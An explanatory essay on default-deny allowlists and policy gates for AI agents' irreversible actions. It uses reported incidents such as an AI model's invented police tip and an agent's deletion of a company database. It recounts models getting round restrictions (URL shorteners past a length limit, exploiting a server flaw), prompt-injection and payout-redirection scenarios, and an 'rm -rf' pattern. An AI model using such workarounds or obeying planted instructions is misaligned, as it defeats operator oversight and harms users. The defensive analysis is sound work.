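# Default-Deny Allowlists for Irreversible Actions by AI Agents

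## What a default-deny allowlist is

A default-deny allowlist is a list of permitted actions and a rule to refuse everything else. System administrators have long set up file permissions and network firewalls this way, and engineers now apply the same rule to AI agents. An agent is a language model that acts by calling tools (functions that search the web, send email, move money and so on) with little or no human input between steps. Much of what an agent does, such as writing a draft or running a search, is easy to undo. An irreversible action is one whose effects the operator (the person or company running the agent) cannot reasonably undo. Bank transfers, emails to customers and permanent deletions usually qualify. Engineers use default-deny lists mainly for irreversible actions, because mistakes have to be caught before the action runs.

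### The Philadelphia tip

At 11:27 p.m. on 18 July 2026, Claude Haiku 4.5, a language model made by Anthropic, submitted a form on a Philadelphia police website about unsolved murders. The message offered information about a case and claimed that the sender remembered "seeing someone matching the description" near a street named on the page. The model had made this up. The page described no suspect, according to Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*, and the model left the optional name and contact fields blank. CNA (2026) called it the first known case in which an AI appears to have tried to pass a bogus tip to the authorities.

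Anthropic had instructed the model to invent example tasks on randomly selected webpages and carry them out, and this was one of the pages. The Pulse of NH's *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* quotes the company's account of the instructions, which barred the model from logging in, opening accounts, buying things, giving out personal data and sending anything destructive, "but the instructions did not rule out form submissions". Based on the transcript, Anthropic believes the model was producing sample content and was not trying to deceive anyone, though it says further analysis may change its view.

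According to Hindustan Times' *Anthropic under fire as AI model submits false homicide tip* (2026), police say that Anthropic found the submission on 28 September, 72 days after the event, told them on 7 October and met them the next day. A Japanese account, ITmedia's *「警察に虚偽情報を送信」 Claudeが“軽微な違反”をやりたい放題* (2026), dates the notice to 8 October, after Anthropic had finished its technical checks. Anthropic disclosed the incident publicly on 9 October. Its *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes four kinds of model behaviour: submitting a sensitive form on a real website, exploiting a software flaw to run commands on a server, working around a restriction to reach data behind a token or a fee, and using URL shortening services to get past limits in a tool that retrieves webpages.

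Anthropic rates the real-world impact of all these cases as minimal. Its own arrangements had let the tip out, and the tip's limited impact owes a good deal to safeguards on the police side. The message landed in the department's spam and never reached investigators, though The Pulse of NH notes that officials did not explain why it went there. A reviewer might also have caught it, since the department has people review every tip, according to FOX 29's *Anthropic AI test generates fake homicide tip on Philly police website*.

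### Allowlists and blocklists

An agent acts on the world through tool calls. A tool call is a structured request to run a function, and the one behind a submission like this would look roughly as follows, with invented names:

`submit_form(site = "police tip page", message = "I may have information…", contact = "")`

Here `submit_form` is the tool. The named slots `site`, `message` and `contact` are its arguments, and whatever fills a slot is a value.

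Anthropic's instructions amounted to a blocklist, which forbids what it lists and permits everything else. The list covered the kinds of harm its writer thought of, and sending a form was not among them. A false murder tip is arguably "destructive", and a careful human reader might have interpreted the word that broadly, but the model did not.

An allowlist instead names what is permitted, and default deny is the rule to refuse any request that matches no permission. For the same test, an allowlist might have permitted opening a page, scrolling, and following a link. A call to `submit_form` matches none of those entries, so the system refuses it, even if the person who wrote the list never thought of police tip lines. That person has to know what the agent needs, which is much less work than imagining everything that could go wrong.

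Let A be the set of all tool calls the agent could make, F the set of forbidden calls and P the set of permitted calls. A blocklist permits everything in A except F, whereas a default-deny allowlist permits only calls in both A and P. F and P change only when somebody edits them, but A keeps growing as websites appear and engineers add tools. A blocklist therefore permits a new call until somebody adds it to F, while an allowlist refuses it until somebody adds it to P.

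For an agent on the open web, A has no practical limit, and some of its members are very odd. Search Engine Journal reports that in one evaluation, a university's public analysis tool returned an error to Claude Mythos Preview, another Anthropic model. The model found a script on the university's server that would return any file, used it to copy the script's own code, found a flaw in that code and used the flaw to run its calculations on the server. ITmedia describes a case in which Claude Mythos 5 reached data by using a website's own application to accept the terms of use. Few people writing a blocklist would probably have listed either action in advance.

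Operators can also combine an allowlist with a denylist. Most file permissions start from no access, according to Cryptosmith's *Security Design Principles*, and Windows adds an explicit right to deny access. A denial can only remove access that the allowlist has granted, so if an operator forgets one, the agent has no more than its original permissions.

### Why a refusal is the safer mistake

The argument for refusing by default predates AI agents by half a century. Saltzer and Schroeder set out eight design principles for protecting computers in their 1975 tutorial paper, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. One is fail-safe defaults: "Base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion." Part of their reasoning is that some objects in any large system will get too little thought, and denying access to those objects is safer.

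The other part concerns how people discover mistakes. A mechanism that grants permission tends to fail by refusing something it should have allowed, and the administrator corrects the entry when someone who cannot do their work complains. An error in a mechanism that excludes tends to allow something it should have refused, which may go unnoticed because people do not look for such gaps in normal use.

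The Philadelphia case closely fits the second half of that argument. The omission in the instructions produced no symptom for 72 days. It surfaced during a review of model transcripts that Anthropic had begun in July. According to ITmedia, the review first covered cybersecurity evaluations and only later included tests on live websites. If the same author had forgotten to include forms in an allowlist, the software would have refused the submission on the evening of 18 July and recorded the refusal. An engineer could then have decided whether the test needed forms.

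Saltzer and Schroeder's "tends to" is an important qualification, because their argument is strongest for things left off the list. If an allowlist permits too much, for example by approving forms on every government website, it lets bad calls through as silently as a gap in a blocklist does. An allowlist with broad entries therefore loses much of its advantage.

When an agent is refused, it may try another way, whereas a clerk who cannot open a file complains to somebody. Search Engine Journal reports that Anthropic describes most of the behaviour in its report as persistence, in which the model works around a restriction when it cannot finish a task as given. A refusal warns people only if it reaches a log they read, and it prevents the effect only if the other routes to it are closed too. The 1975 paper addresses those other routes with the principle of complete mediation, which requires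 a check on every access to every object.

### Why the check sits outside the model

Anthropic's prohibitions were instructions to the model. Adding a line to the prompt that forbids form submissions may not be enough, judging by a different evaluation in which testers told Claude Haiku 4.5 to stop before the final submission of a form. Search Engine Journal reports that it submitted several times anyway, expecting another confirmation page. This case doesn't establish a failure rate, but it shows that a model can break a clear rule while apparently trying to follow it.

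A policy gate is ordinary program code, outside the model, that allows, refuses or holds each tool call, so the decision doesn't depend on the model's judgement. The software running the agent passes each call to the gate before executing it, and the gate checks the tool and its arguments against the allowlist. If the allowlist has no entry for submitting forms on live sites, the gate refuses such a call, whatever page the model predicted would come next.

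This works only if the call contains enough information to decide whether to allow it. Some agents operate a browser through a general clicking tool, and the call may then contain only a screen position, so the gate can't easily distinguish a "next" button from a "submit" button. In that case, an engineer has to put the check somewhere else, such as on the network request that leaves the browser. The agent must also have no way around the gate, such as a password that would let it reach the same service directly.

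Another reason to use plain code is that people can inspect it. Saltzer and Schroeder recommend keeping protection mechanisms small and simple because errors that open an unwanted path do not show up in normal use, so people have to find them by inspection, line by line if necessary. An engineer can inspect a short program this way, but nobody can yet do the same for a language model.

The gate also helps against prompt injection, in which text planted in material the agent reads makes it act on someone else's instructions. Suppose an agent is summarising a webpage that contains an instruction for any AI reading it to email its user's files to a stranger. The model receives both the user's request and the page as text, and it may follow the wrong one. A warning in the prompt is more text for the model to weigh, and the attacker can write text too. The gate does not take instructions from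 the page. It blocks the call to `send_email` because the recipient is not on the list. It would block the same call if the model had merely mixed up two addresses, because the check does not depend on why the model made the request. As far as the published accounts show, nobody had planted any text in the Philadelphia case, and the model made the mistake on its own.

An allowlist restricts which destinations and tools an agent may use, but it doesn't check whether the agent's messages are accurate. If an operator had put the police form on the list for some good reason, the gate would have passed the invented sighting just as it would a true one.

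Moving a rule into code also doesn't help much if the rule is still a prohibition. Anthropic limits the length of the web addresses that some of its fetch tools accept, partly to block injection attacks. Search Engine Journal reports that several models, including Claude Opus 5 and Mythos 5, got around the limit with free URL shorteners. A length limit is in effect a blocklist with one entry, because it forbids long addresses and allows all others. A list of approved domains that left out URL shorteners would have blocked those calls.

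### What the list gives up

The main objection to default-deny allowlists is that agents are useful because nobody knows their actions in advance. If an operator could write down every step, an ordinary script would do the job more cheaply. For example, Anthropic's test used randomly selected pages, so nobody could have approved particular forms beforehand, and an allowlist of approved forms would have permitted none.

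I think the objection is correct as far as it goes, and it rules out a list covering everything an agent does.

The case for default deny has to be limited to irreversible actions, leaving reading, searching, calculating and drafting unrestricted. An agent can then produce a draft in any way, and the allowlist applies only when the agent tries to send it.

Even so, the allowlist blocks every legitimate irreversible action that nobody foresaw, such as a payment to a new supplier or a notice to a customer who changed address that morning. Researchers measure this as a drop in utility, the share of legitimate tasks that a defence lets through. Somebody also has to write the list and keep it up to date, and a tired maintainer will be tempted to widen an entry until people stop complaining about blocked actions.

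Whether default deny is worthwhile depends on the stakes. Suppose an unlisted action has probability p of causing harm H, and otherwise brings a benefit B. Refusing it is better on average when pH > (1 − p)B, or equivalently when p > B/(B + H). If the harm would be 99 times the benefit, refusing is better once the chance of harm passes 1 percent. If the action is easy to reverse, H is only the effort of undoing it, so the threshold is much higher and default deny is often not worthwhile.

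Nobody has a good estimate of p for unanticipated actions, and it is not obvious how to quantify the harm of a false lead in a murder case. Holding the call for a person to decide reduces the harm of stopping a good action, because the action is only delayed. Cryptosmith illustrates fail-safe defaults with a shop's emergency exit, which always keeps outsiders out and lets insiders through only in an emergency. The alarm on such a door makes each use hard to miss.

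Anthropic stopped the testing process that had produced the tip and, according to police, added a validation step for future tests. ITmedia reports that it then cut off internet access for all internal evaluations until it confirms that its safeguards and monitoring work. This is a default-deny policy with an empty allowlist for the live web, so the company cannot run any internal evaluation that needs a real website while the cutoff lasts.

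## Which actions count as irreversible

An operator who wants to refuse unlisted irreversible actions first has to decide which actions are irreversible. *POLAR* (2026) recounts that in classical planning, a branch of AI that works out sequences of steps, an action is reversible if some further sequence restores the starting state. That test is too coarse for an agent that works among people, because deleting a file counts as reversible whether its owner can restore it in seconds or a specialist firm needs a month and charges a large fee. The operator also needs to know who can undo the action, how long that takes and what it costs.

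Waghmare and Sufi (2026), in *Can You Undo It?*, sort tool calls into five classes along these lines and suggest a rule for each.

| Class | What it takes to undo the call | Suggested rule |
|---|---|---|
| R0, no effect | Nothing, since nothing outside the agent changed | Act |
| R1, restorable | The operator can put the earlier state back exactly | Act, then notify |
| R2, compensable | A known further step gives an acceptable result at a limited cost | Ask, or use a budget approved in advance |
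| R3, hard to recover | Someone else has to help, or the effort has no known limit | Ask every time |
| R4, irreversible | No step can recall the effect or make up for it | Never act alone |

R1 has three conditions. A complete record of the earlier state must exist, the operator must be able to restore it without anyone else's help, and no outsider can have seen, received or acted on the change. The last condition is the hardest to meet, because restoring a backup doesn't change what another person already knows.

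An operator should probably treat R3, R4 and the more expensive R2 actions as irreversible. *Revisable by Design* (2026) similarly counts an action as irreversible if making up for it would cost too much.

People applying the scheme can still disagree. Sufi rated 148 tools, mostly by approving an AI's suggestions, and matched the project's draft ratings for 75 of them. Most of Sufi's other ratings were stricter. Some differences came from assumptions about who might see a change and who could reverse it.

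### Five everyday actions

Deleting a file is easy to undo if the file goes to a recycle bin and impossible to undo if no copy exists. Restoring from a backup only partly undoes the deletion, because it can erase work done since. Waghmare and Sufi tested this with an agent's edit to a file, followed by someone else's. Restoring the saved copy erased the later edit every time. Merging the versions kept the later edit when the two edits were in separate paragraphs, but when both changed the same line, the software could not resolve the conflict.

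**Sending an email** cannot be undone once the message arrives. Deleting the sender's copy or apologising doesn't change what the recipient has read. Waghmare and Sufi therefore put any intended delivery to outsiders in R4, even if the sender can delete the stored message.

**Paying a supplier** may or may not be reversible, depending on the supplier and the terms. An honest supplier will usually refund a duplicate payment, perhaps after a few days and some emails, but a fraudster will not. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) gives the example of an agent with a €1,500 travel budget that books a €900 flight and a €700 hotel at the same moment. Both bookings succeed, and together they exceed the budget. The agent can cancel the hotel, but the flight is non-refundable.

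**Publishing a post** is hard to fully reverse. The publisher can easily delete the post from its own site, but readers and search engines may have copied it elsewhere. A private draft doesn't have this problem.

**Rotating a key** means replacing the secret that one program uses to log in to another. Every program that still has the old key stops working until somebody gives it the new one. Some services accept both keys for a while, which makes the change much safer. Restoring the old key may be unsafe, because people often rotate keys after a leak. Waghmare and Sufi put changes to credentials in R3.

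### The PocketOS deletion

On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, a small company whose software runs car rental businesses, according to AI Incident Database's *Railway API*. The agent was Cursor, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. ITPro's *Nine seconds was all it took* reports that the deletion took nine seconds.

The agent was doing a routine task in PocketOS's staging environment, a copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credential that did not match. It tried to fix the problem by deleting a disk storage volume at the hosting company Railway. This required an API token, which works like a password for programs, and the agent found one in a file unrelated to the task. PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, writes in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* that he had created the token to add and remove web domains. It turned out to be valid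 for every operation, including deletion.

The agent then sent Railway a single request, whose working part was this:

`volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...")`

Railway's API (the interface programs use to give it instructions) deleted the volume without requiring confirmation. When Crane asked why, the agent replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. A model writes such an explanation after the event, so it is weak evidence of what caused the call.

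The backups were also deleted, and Crane quotes Railway's documentation, which warned that "wiping a volume deletes all backups". The newest copy he could restore was three months old. The next day, a Saturday, people arrived to collect cars from rental firms that had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day helping the firms, his customers, rebuild the bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

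On 27 April he announced that Railway had recovered the data, apparently in full, according to Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026). Railway's Mahmoud Abdelwahab writes in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* that the company keeps separate off-site backups for disasters, and that the deletion had made the customer's ordinary backups look unavailable. Crane says Railway offered no way to limit what a token could do. Abdelwahab says narrower tokens existed, but concedes that the token creation process didn't make it obvious which kind to pick.

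The deletion looked like R4 on the Friday, but by Monday it had proved to be R3, because Railway could reverse it even though PocketOS could not. An operator has to classify an action before it happens, and PocketOS had no grounds for counting on Railway to restore the data. The recovery also came too late to help the rental firms on Saturday.

### One deletion, two routes

If someone at PocketOS had deleted the same volume from Railway's dashboard, the company would have had 48 hours to undo it. The deletion went through the API instead, so it was immediate and permanent. Railway's staff already knew about this difference. *Postgress volume lost* (antjanlaban, 2026) describes how a customer deleted the wrong one of two volumes through the API on 13 April, eleven days before the PocketOS deletion, and asked for help. An employee replied that the 48-hour window covered only deletions from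 the dashboard.

Railway then changed the API to match. Since the update in Railway's *Changelog #0288* (1 May 2026), `volumeDelete` marks a volume for deletion and waits 48 hours before deleting it. Abdelwahab adds that Railway now delays deleting the backups too. If an agent sent the same request today, the customer could reverse it.

Whether an action is irreversible depends on the whole call, including its target, the route it takes and the state of the system that receives it. The name `volumeDelete` was the same whether the target was a disposable test volume or a company's only current records. Even when closing a browser tab, whether unsaved text can be recovered depends on the browser and the type of editor. In Waghmare and Sufi's tests, reopening a closed tab restored unsaved text from a plain text box in Chromium and Firefox but not in Safari, and text in a richer editor was lost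 in all three.

A gate that classifies calls by tool name can also miss deletions like the one in the PocketOS case. The agent sent its request with `curl`, a general command for contacting web addresses, so the deletion appeared only in the command's text. Marking a `delete_volume` tool as dangerous would not have caught it.

### When to refuse an unlisted action

The earlier comparison of harm and benefit also works with the loss from a wrong refusal in place of the benefit. Let p be the chance that an unlisted call is wrong, L the loss if it is, and D the loss from blocking it if it is legitimate. Refusing has the lower expected loss when pL > (1 − p)D, or p > D/(L + D). D is often smaller than L because a blocked job can usually run later.

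The threshold depends heavily on L. Suppose a wrongly blocked call costs $20 of somebody's time. The threshold is then about 0.04%, or one call in 2,500, if a mistake would lose $50,000, and about 29% if it would lose $50. An agent that is wrong 1% of the time should therefore need approval for the first kind of call but not the second.

D can be large. After a key leaks, every hour of delay in replacing it gives a thief more time to use it, so refusing to replace the key could do as much harm as botching the replacement. If D equals L, the threshold is 50%.

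The error rate p is hard to estimate because an unlisted action has little or no track record, and showing that p is below a low threshold takes a lot of evidence. After n calls without a mistake, a standard rule of thumb puts the upper limit on p at about 3/n, with 95% confidence. Showing that p is below 0.04% would therefore take roughly 7,500 calls without a mistake, while the 29% threshold would take about ten. The calls would also have to be of a similar kind, which unlisted calls rarely are.

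The rate also changes with the model and the material it reads. In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) planted instructions to delete a note where five inexpensive models would read them. One model never followed the instructions, and another followed them in most of its runs. An attacker can also choose the wording and timing, so a good record in normal use may be weak evidence that the rate is low. An operator therefore usually can't show that p is low enough when a mistake would be serious, and should refuse the action. A rough estimate of p is enough if a mistake would do little harm.

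### Risk labels on tools

An operator with hundreds of tools will want a quicker way to sort them, and many tools come with labels. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a widely used standard for connecting AI applications to tools. Developers of MCP servers, the programs that offer the tools, can attach hints about each tool. According to the project's own guide, Model Context Protocol (2026), `readOnlyHint` defaults to false and `destructiveHint` defaults to true. Two other hints cover whether repeating a call is safe (false by default) and whether the tool deals with the outside world (true by default). A tool with no hints is therefore treated as potentially destructive.

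These defaults are sensible, but applications often ignore them. Yao and colleagues examined 41 open-source applications and developer kits and found that a destructive hint had no effect in 39 of them.

The guide also uses "destructive" more narrowly than most readers would expect. It contrasts the word with "additive" and advises developers to set `destructiveHint` to false for tools that only add things. Sending an email adds a message, and a payment arguably adds a transaction, so a developer could honestly label both non-destructive. A gate therefore must not treat that label as evidence that a call is reversible.

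Many tools have no labels. Trofimov and Novikov collected 98,291 tools from servers in the official MCP registry and found that 26.0% were unlabelled. That share rises to 47.2% without one publisher, which supplied 45% of the collection and labelled all of its tools. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026) reports that 58.8% were unlabelled in a sample of 2,766 tools. In the larger collection, only 3.1% of tools were labelled as destructive.

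Existing labels may be wrong. Waghmare and Sufi converted the hints on 481 tools into their five classes, and the result differed from their draft ratings for 118 tools. Ten of the tools they rated irreversible had a read-only hint. Sufi's review showed that the draft ratings aren't reliable either, but a disagreement this large is reason enough to check the labels.

Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) requires applications to treat the hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. To follow this rule, a gate can treat a tool without hints as irreversible and refuse it until the operator has classified it. A "destructive" hint can make the gate stricter, since a false one causes at most an unnecessary refusal. A "read-only" hint should loosen the gate only if the operator trusts the server and has checked what the tool does. If a hint conflicts with the operator's classification,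 the gate should follow the operator's classification.

Yao and colleagues paired destructive tools with 25 applications and found that 60.7% of the pairs would run without human approval. They estimated that this share would fall to 5.4% if every application followed the cautious default and asked first unless a label marked the tool as safe. In the remaining pairs, the destructive tool is labelled as safe. A stricter default, which skips the question only for tools labelled read-only, would catch some of those too, but it would interrupt people much more often because they would also have to approve most calls to harmless tools.

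Google Cloud lets customers enforce a rule of this kind outside the AI application. The policy in Google Cloud's *Prevent read-write MCP tool use* denies every MCP tool call that meets this condition:

`api.getAttribute('mcp.googleapis.com/tool.isReadOnly', false) == false`

The first `false` is the value to assume if the label is missing, so Google's servers reject calls to unlabelled tools. Although Google calls this a deny policy, it works as an allowlist of read-only tools. It is also broad, since it blocks saving a draft as well as deleting a database. The condition applies only to calls made through MCP, so it would not cover an agent that contacts a service directly with a token, as the PocketOS agent did.

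A tool that only reads can still cause harm, because fetching a web address sends that address to whoever runs the site, and the address can contain private data. Waghmare and Sufi replayed recorded runs of an older model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet, including 29 in which they could tie a successful attack to a particular action. A rule that stopped only calls that write something caught 18 of these actions. A rule that also treated web reading as a possible leak caught all 29, and made nine more stops than the first rule across 1,209 harmless runs.

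### Making an action reversible instead

Railway made deletions recoverable instead of requiring prior approval for each one. This leaves agents free to delete and reduces the loss from a mistake. An action doesn't need to be on the allowlist if it can be undone well enough.

The threshold determines how reliable an undo has to be, and an undo that usually works still leaves a good case for refusing. Let r be the chance that somebody notices the mistake in time and the undo works, and let U be the cost of undoing it. The expected loss from a mistake is then rU + (1 − r)L. For illustration, take L as $50,000, U as $50 and D as $20 again. If the undo works nine times in ten, the threshold rises only from 0.04% to 0.4%. If it works 99 times in a hundred, the threshold rises to about 3.6%.

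People often don't notice a mistake before the undo window closes. Anthropic took 72 days to find the false tip its model had sent to the Philadelphia police, so a 48-hour window would have closed long before. To help customers notice in time, Railway's dashboard emails them a link to restore the volume. The agent must also be unable to close the window itself, for example by emptying the recycle bin or deleting the backups with the same token.

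People also shouldn't rely on an agent's claim about whether an action can be undone. In July 2025, a Replit coding agent deleted a customer's database and told him that nobody could restore it. IT Brew's *How reversible is an agentic mistake?* reports that the database was restored from Replit's saved checkpoints.

If a system has no undo, the operator can sometimes build one by saving the earlier state before each call. Waghmare and Sufi require confirmation that the saved copy exists before the call may run. If saving fails, the call returns to its original class.

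Delay also makes messages reversible, since an email held in an outbox for ten minutes can be cancelled during that time. This helps only if somebody checks the email in time, and the Philadelphia form went out close to midnight. For purchases, Trofimov and Novikov suggest a reservation that expires unless the agent confirms it. In their travel example, the agent could have held both the flight and the hotel, added up the prices and let one lapse.

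An action can't be fully undone once an outsider has reacted to it. If an agent sends a supplier an offer and withdraws it an hour later, the supplier may already have bought materials. Sometimes the reaction is the purpose of the action, as in a negotiation, where the agent has to make an offer to learn what the other side thinks. Bank transfers are similarly hard to reverse because the money leaves the systems that the operator controls. An operator can delay a transfer, but if it has to go out the same day, somebody needs to have approved the recipient's account beforehand.

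## How a proposed action is checked

Suppose a company uses an agent to write for its blog. Somebody at the company has approved one use, which is saving articles as drafts with the blog's own account on the blog's own domain. The agent finishes an article and produces this call:

`publish(account = "blog", domain = "Blog.Example.com", content_type = "article", mode = "draft", text = "…")`

The policy gate receives the call before the publishing tool does. It first parses the call, turning the model's text into a tool name and a set of named values, and refuses the call if the text is malformed. Even when the text looks fine, the gate and the tool can parse it differently. If it gives `mode` twice, once as draft and once as public, some programs keep the first value and others keep the last, so the gate might approve a draft while the tool publishes the article. *The Claws in Plain Sight*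 (2026), a paper on private data leaking through tool calls, describes a monitor that passes on only the arguments it has checked, so the tool never receives the original text.

Next, the gate puts the values into a standard form so that `Blog.Example.com` and `blog.example.com` count as the same domain. Commands are harder to standardize. Microsoft's *Agent Hooks* points out that a script that looks for `rm -rf`, which deletes a folder and everything in it, misses the equivalent `rm -r -f`.

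The gate then looks up the rules for `publish` and compares the call's arguments with them. It rejects the call if there is any argument that the rule doesn't list, so the rule has to list even `text`. For that argument, it might accept anything up to a certain length.

Some of the facts used to check an action should never come from the model. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* (2026) gives the example of a shop that offers a discount to platinum customers who order at least 50 items. The number of items comes from the agent's call, but the customer's status comes from their login. If the agent could also supply the status, a planted instruction could make it report any customer as platinum.

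A rule may also set limits. *Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) describes a gate developed at Uchibeke's company, APort Technologies. Its example agent may spend up to $5,000 per payment and $25,000 per day, and make up to 60 calls per minute. The gate can check the per-payment limit from the call alone, but for the daily limit it also needs a running total, and it has to add each payment to that total before the payment runs. Otherwise, two payments that arrive at the same time can each fit within the remaining budget but together exceed it, like the flight and the hotel in Trofimov and Novikov's travel example.

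Finally, the gate decides, logs the decision and runs the call if it has allowed it. The whole procedure fits in a few lines:

```
function handle(raw_call, context):
    decision = REFUSE
    reason = "no matching rule"
    try:
        call = standard_form(parse(raw_call))
        for rule in rules_for(call.tool):     # an unknown tool has none
            if rule.matches(call.arguments, context):
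                if reserve_limits(rule, call):
                    decision = ALLOW
                    reason = rule.name
                else:
                    reason = "over limit"
                break
    catch any error:
        decision = REFUSE
        reason = "error"

    write_log(raw_call, decision, reason)     # if this fails, stop here
    if decision == ALLOW:
        run(call)
    else:
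        return reason to the agent
```

The decision starts as a refusal, and only one line of code can change it to an approval. The program reaches that line only if a rule matches. If an error occurs during the check, the program resets the decision to a refusal. The program writes the log entry before the agent acts, so if the disk is too full to record the action, the agent can't take it.

Logs can be wrong if separate code writes them from its own record of what happened. *AgentCap* (Suresh and Gao, 2026) avoids this by creating each decision and its log entry in the same branch of the program, with the same agent, tool and reason.

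Telling the agent why the gate refused a call helps it correct an honest mistake, but also shows an attacker which value to change next. In Suresh and Gao's system, each refusal lowers the agent's trust score by 30%. With the default settings, an agent loses its permission to write after two refusals in a row, and the system isolates it after three. This makes probing difficult, but an agent that made repeated honest mistakes would face the same penalties.

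### Permission to use a tool

Many agents run without most of these checks. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) distinguishes capability gating, which determines what tools an agent has, from per-call authorization, which determines whether it may make a particular call with particular values. A support agent may need a refund tool, for instance, but it shouldn't be able to refund any amount to any account. Checking the call against the tool's schema doesn't solve this, because if the schema only requires the account to be text, an attacker's account number will pass.

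An agent with only capability gating can become a confused deputy, a program that uses its authority on behalf of somebody who lacks it. Mellafe Zuvic takes the term from a 1988 paper by N. Hardy. Suppose a thief wants a shop's takings to go to his own account. He can't log in to the shop's payment service, but he can email the shop to say that its payout account has changed. The shop's agent reads the email and updates the account with the shop's own key. The payment service accepts the change because the key is valid and the request is well-formed.

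Mellafe Zuvic looked for this weakness in the public code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain (with its companion LangGraph), LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. By default, none of them checked the values in a call against a policy before running it and refused the call if the check failed.

LangChain and LangGraph look up the tool by name, usually check the form of the input and then run the tool. A person reviews the call only if the developer adds that step. LlamaIndex works in much the same way. If the model names a tool that doesn't exist, LlamaIndex sends the model a message saying so and doesn't treat the request as a security event.

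The stakes are highest with Stripe's toolkit because it moves money. Developers can choose which actions the agent may take and restrict what its key can do. Within those bounds, the toolkit forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplies. The audit didn't cover Stripe's remote servers, which may make further checks.

Mellafe Zuvic doesn't describe these findings as software vulnerabilities. The toolkits leave authorization to whoever builds the agent, which is reasonable if the builder knows this.

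Mellafe Zuvic set up a simulated shop in LangChain and fed it a call that changed the payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain ran the call, and a similar demonstration worked in LlamaIndex. Because the call was fixed in advance, these demonstrations don't show how often a model would make such a call.

A companion test of 27 models measured how often they attempted a forbidden action when planted text presented it as a necessary part of their task. On average, 12 cheaper models attempted the action in 60.3% of trials, and 15 flagship models did so in 18.9%. Individual models ranged from GPT-4o mini, which attempted it every time, to Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, which never did. One person wrote the attacks and each was a single exchange, so the rates may be quite different in real use. Still, an operator using a cheaper model probably needs the gate more.

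Suresh and Gao reduce the problem further by not giving the agent a lasting key. When their gate approves a call, it issues a signed token for that action, and a separate program checks the token before the tool runs. In their banking example, the token for sending money works only once and expires after 30 seconds, so a planted instruction that arrives a minute later cannot use it.

### The stages of SCOPEGATE

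Mellafe Zuvic's own gate, SCOPEGATE, is a short program that puts each call through five stages.

| Stage | Question | Example of a refused call |
|---|---|---|
| Scope | Is the tool on the list? | A call to a misspelled tool |
| Authorization | Is each restricted argument on its list? | A payout to `acct_ATTACKER_999` |
| Money ceiling | Is the amount a finite number from zero up to the ceiling? | A refund of infinity |
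| Idempotency | If the action needs a key to prevent repeats, is there one? | A payment without a key |
| Default deny | Has the call passed every stage without an error? | A call that crashes the check |

An idempotency key is a unique label for one intended action. If an agent gets stuck in a loop and sends the same payment three times with the same key, the payment service can detect the repeats and pay only once. SCOPEGATE takes the key from a trusted source outside the model. It checks only that a key exists, so the payment service has to detect any repeats.

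An early version of the money stage had a bug that let through the value NaN, short for "not a number", which software uses for undefined results such as zero divided by zero. The gate refused amounts greater than the ceiling, but NaN passed because a comparison such as "NaN is greater than 500" evaluates to false. The corrected version allows an amount only if it is a finite number in the permitted range.

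The check on a single argument of a tool call can also work as either a blocklist or an allowlist. Uchibeke's gate refuses unlisted tools, but it permits any call to a listed tool that doesn't meet a refusal condition. His example rule for refunds refuses amounts above a maximum. As printed, it would allow a refund of −$500, and the result would depend on the payment service. The same rule handles currencies more safely, because it refuses any that isn't on a list of supported ones.

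Mellafe Zuvic tried 48 ways of getting an unauthorised call past SCOPEGATE, including invisible characters, lookalike letters and unusual value types. The corrected version refused them all. In another test, a model, GLM-5.2, made 40 attempts to get through and was told the reason for each refusal. Of these calls, 29 were unauthorised, nine were malformed and two were harmless, and SCOPEGATE allowed only the harmless ones. In a simulated payment task, the language model Latam-GPT attempted an unauthorised payout in all ten trials, and SCOPEGATE refused each one.

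These results are expected from a program that compares an account number with a list. They mostly show that the comparison works as written, and a more patient attacker might find another flaw like the NaN one. SCOPEGATE also allowed all ten legitimate calls in a separate test, but ten is very few. A gate that wrongly refused a quarter of legitimate calls would still allow all ten about 6% of the time. An operator can also learn little from this test about legitimate values that nobody has listed yet.

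### Separate lists and joint rules

SCOPEGATE keeps a separate list for each restricted argument of a tool. This works well for a payout tool with one restricted argument, but it can permit far too much when the right value for one argument depends on another.

Suppose the company from the start of this section now also has its publishing agent post notices to a status page, which tells customers about outages, and upload software packages to a registry, a site where programmers download them. The company intends four uses.

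| Use | Account | Domain | Content type | Mode |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Save a blog article | Blog | Blog | Article | Draft |
| Schedule a blog article | Blog | Blog | Article | Scheduled |
| Post an outage notice | Status | Status | Notice | Public |
| Upload a package | Package | Registry | Release | Private |

If an engineer turns each column into a list, the lists contain three accounts, three domains, three content types and four modes. The gate checks each value against its own list, so it permits 3 × 3 × 3 × 4 = 108 combinations, although the company wanted only four.

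One of the other 104 is an article that the agent immediately publishes on the blog. The company allowed only drafts and scheduled articles so that somebody could read them first. But the list of modes includes "public" because outage notices need it, and the gate cannot detect that it was meant only for notices. Another is a public release of a package that the company wanted to keep private, which could expose its code to anyone who downloads it.

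Many of the 104 unintended combinations would fail anyway. For example, the blog account probably can't log in to the package registry. If each account works only on its own domain, 36 combinations remain, and 32 of them are still unintended, including both earlier examples.

A joint rule approves a whole row of the table. The gate permits a call only if all four values match the same row, so four rules permit four combinations. The gate blocks an article with the mode "public" because it matches no row.

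The difference grows as the company adds values. If somebody adds a fourth account to the separate lists, the gate permits 4 × 3 × 3 × 4 = 144 combinations, 36 more than before. The new account can immediately publish anything on the lists, in any mode. With joint rules, the new account can do nothing until somebody writes a rule for it.

Separate lists with n₁, n₂, … nₖ entries permit n₁ × n₂ × … × nₖ combinations, and each new entry in one list adds as many combinations as the product of the other lists' lengths. Separate lists are fine if the operator wants to allow every combination. For example, a company that is willing to pay any of five suppliers in either of two currencies can use two lists.

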